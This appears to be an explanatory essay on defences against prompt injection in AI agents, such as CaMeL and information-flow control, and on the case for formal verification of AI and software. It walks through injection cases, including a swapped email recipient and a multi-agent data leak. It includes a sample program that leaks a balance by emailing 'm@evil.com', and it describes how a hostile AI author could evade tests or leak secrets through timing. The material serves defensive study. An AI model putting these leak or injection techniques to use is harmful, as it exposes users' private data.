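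Developers can train models to ignore injected instructions, which makes attacks harder but does not guarantee that they will fail. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) warns that a model trained on known attacks may still be vulnerable to new ones. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on a public competition with 272,000 attack attempts against 13 leading models. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Even at 0.5%, an attacker who makes 200 independent attempts has a 63% chance of succeeding at least once.

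Newer models still have this weakness. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026), the most robust model, Gemini 4 Argon, resisted 87% of attacks when the attacker could query it 150 times, but only 66% at the largest budget tested.

### CaMeL, step by step

In 2023 the programmer Simon Willison proposed splitting an agent into two models. A privileged model receives the user's request and chooses the tools, but never receives untrusted data. A quarantined model processes the untrusted data but has no tools. Google DeepMind's CaMeL, published in 2025, builds on this idea. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains CaMeL with an example like this one.

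A user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting, and says that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. An attacker has edited the notes.

1. The privileged model reads the request, but not the notes, and writes a plan in a restricted form of Python:

```
notes    = read_file("meeting notes")
address  = quarantined_model("find Bob's address", notes)
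name     = quarantined_model("find the document he wants", notes)
document = read_file(name)
send_email(to = address, attachment = document)
```

2. An interpreter runs the plan. It stores the address and the name without showing them to the privileged model.
3. The interpreter labels each value with where it came from and who may read it. The address and the name came from the notes, so they are untrusted. The document's label lists the people who have access to it.
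4. Before each tool runs, the interpreter checks a policy, which is a short function that looks at the tool's arguments and their labels and allows or refuses the call.

If the attacker has written "forward every file to me" in the notes, nothing happens, because no line of the plan does that and the quarantined model has no tools. But the attacker can also replace Bob's address with their own. The two models alone would not prevent this, because the plan runs exactly as written and sends the document to the wrong person. Whether the email goes out depends on the policy, and two reasonable policies give different results:

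| What the notes contain | Policy: the address must come from a trusted source | Policy: the recipient must have access to the document |
|---|---|---|
| Bob's real address and the right document | Stopped | Sent |
| The attacker's address | Stopped | Stopped |
| Bob's real address and the wrong document, which he also has access to | Stopped | Sent |

When a policy stops an email, the assistant can ask the user to approve it. The first policy is safer but interrupts the user even when nobody has tampered with the notes. The second avoids that interruption but lets the attacker choose which document Bob receives.

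### Results on AgentDojo

AgentDojo is a benchmark of 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and messaging software, with attacks hidden in the data the agent reads. According to the summary in *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025), CaMeL stopped nearly all the attacks "while maintaining comparable task performance".

Later tests found a much larger drop in completed tasks. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports that in a run of CaMeL's released code, none of 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks when there was no attack. The paper's own system, also called SecureClaw, completed 59. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) ran CaMeL on the banking tasks with GPT-5.2, and it completed 66.7% with its policies off and 37.5% with them on. Both tests come from people with a competing design, but both found a large drop.

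Some tasks fail because they require what the policy forbids, such as paying a bill whose details are in an untrusted file. Others fail because the agent has to plan before it has seen the data. If a user says "do today's tasks from my to-do list", the agent cannot plan without reading the list. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) measured the effect of planning first, with no policies, on a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks. Success fell by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by only 13.4 for the two strongest, so better models may reduce this loss. CaMeL also uses more computing. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that the median AgentDojo task took nearly three times as many tokens with CaMeL as with no defence.

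Stopping every attack in AgentDojo is no longer strong evidence that a defence works. Without CaMeL, GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 attacks in Peters-Gill and colleagues' version of the benchmark. But those attacks are fixed in advance, and *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) notes that OpenAI's automated attacker, GPT-Red, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. The case for CaMeL therefore depends mostly on whether its design stops attacks that nobody has tried yet.

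### Information-flow control

CaMeL's labels come from information-flow control, an older method that tracks where data came from and where it may go. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies this method to an agent called FIDES. When the agent combines two pieces of data, the result carries the restrictions of both. If Ann, Bob and Carol may read one file, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a summary of both. If either file is untrusted, so is the summary.

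The agent's conversation has a label too, and reading one untrusted email would make every later decision untrusted. FIDES avoids this by storing the email in a variable and showing the model only the variable's name. The model can then send a narrow question to a quarantined model, such as whether the email requests a meeting, and see the yes-or-no answer. An attacker can still make that answer wrong, but a single bit cannot carry an instruction. This lets FIDES adapt its plan to what it finds, within limits.

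Costa and colleagues prove explicit secrecy, the property that secret data never flows directly into anything an outsider can see. This is weaker than noninterference, because an outsider may still learn something from which tools the agent calls. They consider noninterference too restrictive because it would roughly mean banning every publicly visible action once the agent had read a secret.

*Flowsh* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) extends this approach to agents that run shell commands, whose effects are hard to predict. The system runs each command in a sandbox and records which files the command opens and which sites it contacts. It applies changes to files only after checking them against the policy. A network request cannot be undone, so the system checks each one before sending it. This includes requests that only read a web page, because the page's address can contain a secret.

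Flowsh asked for approval 5.8 times less often per completed task than a loosely configured sandbox on office-style tasks, and 22.5 times less often on command-line tasks. But its completion rates were 7.9 and 9.7 percentage points lower, respectively. None of 19 prompt-injection attacks succeeded when Flowsh ran without a user to approve requests. The drop in requests matters for security because people stop reading requests when they get too many. Kim and colleagues cite Anthropic's figure that users approve about 93% of Claude Code's requests.

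### Gaps in the tracking

Labels protect data only if the code that tracks them is right. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's interpreter could lose track of a secret, as in this simplified program:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                  rich = False
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes False and the interpreter marks it as secret. The interpreter then skips the line that would change `rich`, so it never marks `rich` as secret, even though its value depends on the balance. The policy allows the email, and the recipient learns that the balance is high. An honest user's request is unlikely to produce such a plan, so this is more a gap in the guarantee than a ready-to-use attack.

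They found another leak in the code that retries a failed plan, which runs outside the interpreter and has no labels. An attempt can reveal one bit of a secret through whether a policy blocked the attempt, and repeated attempts can reveal the rest.

Garby and colleagues wrote an interpreter in Lean, with a machine-checked proof that every program in its language satisfies noninterference, including programs that a model writes. The proof does not cover what an observer learns from whether a program finishes. Their agent, Randori, can also mark an untrusted value as trusted ("endorse" it) when the user's request calls for that. The table compares the agents on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks with no attack.

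| Agent | Model | Completed, policies off | Completed, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent (Costa and colleagues) | GPT-4o | 98.8% | 37.5% |
| FIDES (Costa and colleagues) | GPT-4o | 65.0% | 52.5% |
| CaMeL (Garby and colleagues) | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 37.5% |
| Randori (Garby and colleagues) | GPT-5.2 | Always on | 75.0% |

The tests used few tasks and different models and policies, so small differences between results mean little. But Randori's score suggests that strict policies cause much of the drop in scores, and that allowing exceptions can recover it.

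Using several agents creates another weakness. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system in which one CaMeL agent read a database of job applicants, a second summarised the result, and a third sent the summary to a colleague. An attacker had hidden an instruction in the database. The second agent put the summary into its request to the third, which treated the whole request as coming from its user and emailed the data to the attacker, even though each agent had followed its own rules. The fix is to send instructions and data through separate channels and keep the labels attached. On their version of AgentDojo, this reduced the attack success rate from 0.2% to zero.

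### Checking the policy or the plan before the agent runs

CaMeL's policies are ordinary code and may contain mistakes. *VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) has a model write both a policy function and its contract from a natural-language request, such as "the agent cannot send emails to non-company addresses". The system asks the user about ambiguities, tests the function, then uses Nagini, a verifier for Python, to prove that the function meets its contract. When the agent runs, the function checks each action before the agent takes it.

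On a benchmark of attacks against agents using Gemini 2.5 Flash, VeriGuard reduced the average attack success rate from 51.9% to zero. Asking a model whether each action broke the rules also reduced it to zero, but the agents then completed only 40.2% of their tasks, compared with 63.3% under VeriGuard. When Miculicich and colleagues added VeriGuard's parts one at a time, the attack success rate reached zero before they added the proof. The results therefore support using precise policies, but they don't show that proving them made a difference.

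The system is also vulnerable when the agent runs, because a language model reads the proposed action and fills in the function's arguments. If an attacker can get the model to leave one recipient off the list, the function will work correctly but approve an incomplete list. Taking the arguments directly from the tool call, as CaMeL does, avoids this.

Other rules concern the order of events. A company might require its incident team to approve any plan that disconnects a computer from the network. CaMeL would detect a missing approval only when it reached that step. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) translates the whole plan into a finite set of states and uses a model checker to examine every path before any tool runs. If a path breaks the rule, the planner receives it as a counterexample and tries to repair the plan. The method can also check that something eventually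 happens, for example that every open incident ticket gets closed. Because the method allows for any number of passes through a loop, it may reject a safe plan.

### Verified monitors for learned controllers

Control engineers faced a similar problem before language models existed. In 2001 Lui Sha described an arrangement called Simplex, in which a complex controller runs a machine while a simple, trusted one stands by. A monitor switches to the simple controller before the machine reaches a state it could not recover from.

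Suppose a learned controller drives a car towards a stationary obstacle at distance d, and the monitor makes a decision every T seconds. If v is the speed, a the greatest possible acceleration and b the weakest braking the car can rely on, the monitor lets the learned controller act only when:

```
v × T  +  a × T² / 2  +  (v + a × T)² / (2 × b)  ≤  d
```

The left side is how far the car would travel if it accelerated as hard as possible until the next decision and then braked. At 20 metres per second, with T = 0.1, a = 2 and b = 5, this is about 42.8 metres. If the obstacle is closer than that, the monitor brakes. If the car can stop in time at the start, it can stop in time after every decision, whatever the learned controller does. In 2018 Nathan Fulton and André Platzer used verified monitors of this kind with controllers that learn by trial and error.

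The proof assumes that the brakes work and that d is correct. If a neural network estimates d from a camera image, the guarantee again depends on that network.

For an AI agent, the equivalent of braking is refusing an action. This is usually safe, but stopping halfway can cause damage, for example if an agent has renamed a file but not updated the settings that refer to it. Flowsh therefore applies all of a command's file changes or none of them.

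### What the proof covers and what an attacker can still do

If the checking code is correct, the labels on incoming data are right, and every action has to pass the check, these designs can support a theorem of this form:

```
for every output the models could produce,
and all untrusted data that the tools could return:
    every action the system carries out satisfies the policy
```

With information-flow control, the policy can also forbid data flows, such as a confidential file reaching someone who isn't allowed to read it. The theorem holds for any model, including one that an attacker fully controls, so nobody has to verify the model. But it doesn't guarantee that the assistant will do what the user asked.

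The policy itself may be wrong. Flowsh's example configuration treats software from package repositories as trusted, so if an attacker got malicious code into one of those repositories, the system would treat that code as trusted too.

An attacker can also do harm through actions that the policy permits. Attacks on Randori succeeded in only two of 1,296 runs, both on the same task, in which the user asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file. The attacker had replaced the bill, but paying it still matched the user's request, and Randori had endorsed the file's contents so that the agent could carry out that request. Without endorsement, Randori blocked the attack but also could not pay genuine bills from a file.

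The assistant can mislead a user without taking any forbidden action. An injected instruction can make the quarantined model leave a warning out of a summary or reverse its meaning. The policy still allows the assistant to show the user the summary, and the user may make a bad decision because of it.

Finally, the theorem doesn't cover flaws in the software around the check. Suppose the tool that opens the meeting notes contains the file reader's original flaw. A crafted file could then overrun the buffer and run the attacker's code inside the tool. That code could send the document without the interpreter checking whether this is allowed.

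## Do learned systems lack security guarantees unless formal methods supply them?

Some advocates of proof argue that a learned system, meaning one whose behaviour comes from training, has no security guarantee unless formal methods supply it. Written out, the argument has three premises and a conclusion:

1. Training improves a model's average performance on a sample of inputs.
2. An attacker looks for the input on which the model performs worst.
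3. Testing covers too few inputs to show that no bad input exists.
4. Therefore, only a proof gives assurance against an attacker.

### From the average to the worst case

Training and security depend on different quantities:

```
training reduces:      the average error over the sample
security depends on:   the largest error over every input an attacker could send
```

A model's failure rate on random prompts can be tiny even when its failure rate against an attacker who chooses the prompts is as large as possible. Suppose a model misbehaves on one in a trillion 20-token prompts. With GPT-2's vocabulary there are about 10⁹⁴ such prompts, so about 10⁸² of them would work for an attacker.

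However, the first premise describes the goal of training, which may differ from the result. A network trained on examples of addition could learn to add every pair of numbers correctly. Some methods also train against the worst input within a small distance of each example. So the premise shows that ordinary training does not guarantee security, but not that any particular model is insecure.

The premise about attackers is hard to dispute, and attackers are getting stronger. Kovacs (2026), in *UK's Hardest AI Hacking Test Doesn't Survive Its First Round*, reports that OpenAI's GPT-6 and GPT-6.2 Astra beat the hardest cyber range (a simulated target for practising attacks) that the UK's AI Security Institute has built. But attackers still have to find the bad input, which can be impractical even when one exists. For example, trying every 128-bit encryption key at a billion guesses a second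 would take about 10²² years.

The premise about testing also holds for any system with many possible inputs. *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024) points out that OpenAI evaluated ChatGPT for months, but users got past its safety measures within a day of its release. Testing can still support a statistical claim. In the paper's example, a car that drives a million miles without human intervention probably fails less than once per million miles. This slightly overstates the evidence, because a car that averages one failure per million miles has a 37% chance of driving that far without one. The claim also becomes unreliable if conditions change, for instance if other drivers become more aggressive around driverless cars.

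Combining safeguards can greatly reduce the failure rate. If two independent filters each miss one harmful input in a thousand, together they miss one in a million. This calculation can fail when an attacker searches for inputs that get past both.

Whether the conclusion follows depends on what "assurance" means. If it means an argument that covers every possible input, then almost by definition only a proof of some kind will do, but the proof need not involve formal methods. For example, a model that has never had access to a password can't look it up and reveal it, and this is clear without a proof assistant. If "assurance" means good grounds for confidence, the conclusion is too strong, because a long record of failed attacks can also provide those grounds.

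### Does a missing proof mean there is a way in?

Tegmark and Omohundro (2023), in *Provably safe systems*, make a more ambitious version of the argument. They start from Gödel's completeness theorem, which says that any statement true in every situation that fits a set of axioms can be proved from those axioms. Because computers have a finite number of states, Tegmark and Omohundro conclude that any safety property without a proof can be violated. A powerful AI may find a way to violate it and, if it is malicious, will use it.

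Any true property of a finite machine has a proof, since one could list every state the machine can reach and check each one. But a machine with a gigabyte of memory has 2 to the power of 8 billion possible states, a number with about 2.4 billion digits. So a proof might exist that no one can write down, and failing to find one doesn't show that the machine has a flaw.

Not every violation gives an attacker something to use. The statement "nobody without the key will ever read this message" cannot be proved, because someone could guess the key by luck. In practice, even a very capable AI would not guess it.

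### Code, model and system

The slogan that learned systems have no guarantees without formal methods combines claims about three different things.

| What the claim is about | Which premises apply | Whether only proof will do |
|---|---|---|
| Code that an AI writes | The premises about attackers and testing apply, as they do to human-written code. The model's training no longer matters once the program exists. | Proof can rule out stated flaws. Memory-safe languages and automatic checks can also rule out some classes of flaw. |
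| The model's own behaviour | All three apply. | A proof would help, but for most of the properties people care about, nobody can write the specification or complete the proof. |
| The whole system | The premises about attackers and testing apply throughout. Training matters where the result depends on the model's output. | Proofs about the surrounding code can limit what any output does, but an attacker can still cause harm through permitted actions. |

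Evidence for one claim only weakly supports the others. For example, a model with no guarantee can write a program with a proven guarantee, but that proof doesn't make the model trustworthy.

### Proofs from an author nobody trusts

Tegmark and Omohundro's case is much stronger when it concerns who writes the code. They build on proof-carrying code, which George Necula proposed in the 1990s. In their version, it would work like this:

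1. People write the specification, with help from AI.
2. An AI system writes a program and a proof that the program meets the specification.
3. A proof checker that the AI did not write checks the proof.
4. The hardware runs the program only if the proof passes.

A proof checker can be very small; one for the proof system Metamath has about 300 lines of Python. Its result doesn't depend on who wrote the proof or why, so people could safely use a proof from a model they suspect of working against them. They couldn't rely on tests in the same way, because a hostile author could write a program that behaves well whenever it detects a test.

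Dalrymple argues in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that a model rewarded for passing tests during training can learn to satisfy only those tests, whereas a proof has to cover every case.

A hostile author can still exploit whatever the specification leaves out. Suppose the file reader's specification requires memory safety and correct results but doesn't restrict timing. The author could make the program leak a bit of the server's encryption key by pausing briefly whenever that bit is 1, and the proof would still pass. An honest programmer would be unlikely to do this by accident, so a specification for code from untrusted authors has to be stricter. In *Safeguarded AI*, Ammann expects that as AI produces more of the proofs, people will have to rely more on specifications and assumptions.

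### Guaranteed safe AI

Dalrymple and colleagues extend the idea from programs to the effects an AI system has on the world. Their approach, guaranteed safe AI, has three parts:

- A world model describes mathematically how the system's outputs affect its surroundings.
- A safety specification defines which effects are acceptable.
- A verifier produces a proof that the system meets the specification within the world model, or a limit on the probability that it doesn't.

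The monitor for a learned car controller fits this pattern. Its world model is the equation for stopping distance, its specification is that the car never hits the obstacle, and the proof covers any decision the controller makes. The AI can remain a black box as long as the verifier can check its outputs.

World models and specifications vary in strength. At the weak end, the world model is a trained simulator whose workings nobody can understand, and the specification is written in ordinary language and interpreted by a second AI. Dalrymple and colleagues don't think either provides the guarantees they want. At the strong end, engineers prove that the world model follows from the laws of physics, and the specification covers everything people might want. Most practical proposals lie between these extremes.

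Human behaviour is too complex to predict in detail, so one proposal is to have the world model list a set of things people might do and require the verifier to cover all of them. This strengthens the guarantee, but if the set is too broad, no useful system can satisfy the specification.

They also explain how errors in the world model weaken a guarantee. If the model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step, a proof covering n steps holds in reality with probability at least:

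```
(1 − ε)ⁿ
```

With an error rate ε of one in a million per step, a proof covering 10,000 steps would still hold with probability 99%. At one in a thousand, a proof covering only 1,000 steps would hold with probability 37%. An attacker can steer the system towards situations that the model describes badly, so ε would have to hold in those situations as well as in ordinary use.

### Why not keep searching and patching?

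In *LLMs + Security = Trouble*, Livshits (2026) criticises using one AI to check or attack code written by another. Triggering the most valuable flaws often requires a long chain of unlikely conditions, so a search with a fixed budget misses many of them. Defenders also have to avoid damaging their own systems, while a real attacker can concentrate on one target for as long as it takes.

Livshits adds that code that resists today's models may not resist next year's. Anthropic's study of logic bugs supports this, since newer Claude models found many bugs that an older one missed.

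However, Livshits doesn't think proofs fit the way many people now write software with AI. Developers who accept every change a model suggests are unlikely to examine a specification carefully. With a tool called Astrogator, the user confirms a precise version of the request, and the tool compares it with the model's code. In a test with 1,260 programs, it verified 83% of the correct ones, so a developer would have to judge the rest.

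Livshits prefers rules that a model can't break when generating code, such as requiring a bounds check before every array access. That check would stop the file reader's bad write without a separate proof for each program, although someone would still have to show that the rule works.

Some rules are hard to enforce on a model that writes one token at a time, because a half-written program that hasn't yet removed dangerous characters from a user's input may still do so later. Livshits therefore sees promise in diffusion models, which generate the whole program together. Many security repairs are one or two lines long, which favours this approach, but whether an ownership check is missing depends on the application's own rules, which no standard check contains.

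*You Can't Patch Your Way Out of This*, from the formal-methods company Galois, makes a broader case against patching. It notes that Mozilla fixed more security bugs in Firefox in one month than in the previous 15 months combined. It argues that attackers need only one good bug, while defenders need to find them all. It also reports that attackers used Claude and GPT models in an attempted intrusion into the water infrastructure of Monterrey, a metropolitan area of more than five million people.

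Galois is right that better search tools help attackers too, but its claim that a proof is "the last patch you need" is too strong. Programs change, and a proof covers only stated properties. Attackers also often need more than one bug, as Mozilla says of Firefox. In a stable program, patching could catch up with the flaws if different searchers keep finding the same ones. This is less likely where developers, or their AI agents, add new code faster than anyone can examine it.

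### Where the programmes stand in 2026

The UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA) funds a programme called Safeguarded AI, which Dalrymple led until Ammann took over. ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* gives the programme's budget as £59 million. The programme originally aimed to build a "gatekeeper", which ARIA describes as an AI system for understanding and reducing the risks of other AI agents. The gatekeeper would have offered quantitative guarantees like those people expect for nuclear power and passenger aviation.

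In late 2025 ARIA cancelled the part of the programme that would have developed specialised AI for this work, because general-purpose models were improving so quickly that Dalrymple expected them to acquire many of the necessary skills anyway. ARIA moved £18 million from that part into tools for modelling and proof. Ammann says ARIA also changed direction because timely international agreement to use gatekeepers had become less likely.

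ARIA also dropped a planned funding call for uses in physical systems. The original plan was to demonstrate a safer way of deploying powerful AI than a general-purpose chat service. ARIA says that plan relied on the possibility that high-risk models would not become openly available, and that this proved wrong.

The programme now focuses first on cybersecurity. In 2025 Dalrymple's leading idea for a demonstration was a verified firewall for power grids, water systems and air traffic control, which increasingly communicate over the internet instead of dedicated wires. A funding call that closed in July 2026 sought teams to build verified components and other teams to attack them. ARIA's *Funded projects* lists further funding for security work. The programme is due to end in 2027.

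ARIA has moved from guarantees about what AI does in the world towards guarantees about software. It did so because of the pace of AI development and politics, so the move doesn't show that the original idea was impossible. But nobody has yet demonstrated the kind of gatekeeper ARIA first proposed.

Companies are concentrating on software and hardware too, and Alcides Fonseca's *Full-stack verification is the new trend* describes several recent efforts. Harmonic uses an AI agent to verify programs and chip designs, SF-Tensor is describing the instructions of Nvidia's graphics processors in Lean, and the start-up &Truth plans to prove AI-written software correct.

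### Proofs about the physical world

Dickson (2024), in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety*, objects that proofs apply to symbols, while the dangers people worry about are physical. NASA's Jet Propulsion Laboratory used formal verification on the software that landed the Perseverance rover on Mars. That verification covered bugs in the software, but not the landing itself or a faulty transistor in the computer. Dickson cites figures showing that about half of Mars missions have failed and that software accounts for about 20% of the failure risk. On those figures, perfect software would lower the failure rate from 50% to about 40%.

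The disagreement is clearest over machines that make DNA. Tegmark and Omohundro want them to operate only with a proof of safety. Dickson replies that proving a new virus harmless would require simulating years of its effects on a human body. In 2022 researchers simulated a very simple cell for 20 minutes, and a human body has about 36 trillion cells, most of them far more complex. A reader of Dickson's post answers that Dalrymple and colleagues proposed something narrower, a machine that provably cannot make certain pathogens.

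Engineers could plausibly prove that the machine's software rejects every sequence on a fixed list. That proof would be useful, but it wouldn't cover dangerous sequences missing from the list. A guarantee that also covers those needs the biology that Dickson describes.

Omohundro replied to Dickson that engineers don't need to verify every possible system, because they can design systems so that proofs are feasible. Engineers already have reliable models of bridges and machines, and a proof assistant could check that a design follows the rules. Omohundro accepts that nobody can prevent all physical failures, and aims to limit their probability and the damage they cause.

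The point about design is well supported for software. The seL4 kernel and agents such as CaMeL have guarantees because their designers kept the critical part small. The point is weaker for physical engineering, because bridge rules are written for designers who want the bridge to stand. Someone who wanted it to fall could follow every rule and look for a weakness they don't cover.

Designing a system so that it can be verified is also difficult when the useful part is a neural network. Tegmark and Omohundro expect AI to extract what networks have learned and rewrite it as ordinary code that people can verify. Zac Hatfield-Dodds, who maintains a widely used testing library, objects in his talk *Formal Verification is Overrated* that such code won't match machine learning at the tasks machine learning does best. The most capable models of 2026 are still neural networks, which so far supports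 his objection.

Dalrymple and colleagues reject the objection that the world is too complex to model. They argue that if an AI is dangerous because it can reliably carry out complicated plans, then sufficiently accurate world models must be possible. But an attacker needs to predict the results of only one successful plan, while a verifier has to cover every plan an attacker might try. They argue more convincingly that every safety method relies on assumptions about the world, and that a world model at least makes them explicit. Hatfield-Dodds replies that someone still has to show that the assumptions are true, and would prefer to spend the time examining specific threats directly.

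Dickson also asks how anyone would know that a proof describes the machine they are using. A chatbot's users, for example, can't inspect the computer it runs on. Tegmark and Omohundro propose hardware that detects tampering and erases its cryptographic keys, but people would have to trust that hardware. Ammann lists this among the programme's open problems.

### Is cryptography a good precedent?

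Cryptographers have long tried to prove that their methods resist an attacker who chooses the worst case. Many of their proofs, like the computational ones for Signal, depend on a problem that researchers believe is hard to solve. RSA, a widely used encryption method, is secure only if nobody can factor very large numbers efficiently. No one has proved that ordinary computers can't do this, and the main evidence that they can't is that many people have tried for decades and failed.

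Even here, confidence comes partly from failed attacks, which counts against the claim that only proof gives assurance. The failed attacks are especially informative because they all concern one small, precisely stated problem.

Some AI safety researchers think theory will help less with deep learning than it has with cryptography. Cryptographers can choose a method because they know how to prove something about it, whereas developers choose a network because it performs well. Nobody knows of a hard mathematical problem that an attacker would have to solve to make a language model misbehave.

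There may also be limits that better theory can't remove. *Limitations on Safe, Trusted, Artificial General Intelligence* (Panigrahy and Sharan, 2025) defines a safe system as one that never makes a false claim and a trusted system as one that people assume is safe. It shows that no system can be both safe and trusted while always matching or exceeding human ability. Young's *On the Computational, Informational, and Physical Foundations for AI Safety* argues that even simplified forms of the problem of a system verifying its own meaning are NP-complete, like the exact verification of ReLU networks.

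These results rule out very general guarantees but, like Rice's theorem, leave room for proofs about narrower properties.

### Most ordinary software has no proof either

Conventional software can lack security guarantees too. Nobody has proved that Linux or a major web browser is secure, and Böhme's advice to assume that flaws remain applies to any large system.

The reasons for it differ, though. Many ordinary programs could have a proof of memory safety if somebody paid for it, and Anthropic's work on 123 libraries shows that the price is falling. When engineers find a flaw like the file reader's, they can add one line and prove that no file can cause the bad write.

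A developer who finds a prompt that makes a model misbehave can train the model to refuse it, but can't show that the training covers every rewording of the prompt or that it hasn't caused a new failure elsewhere. More proof work would not currently solve this, because for most such failures there is no precise specification to check the model against and no verifier that can handle a model of its size.
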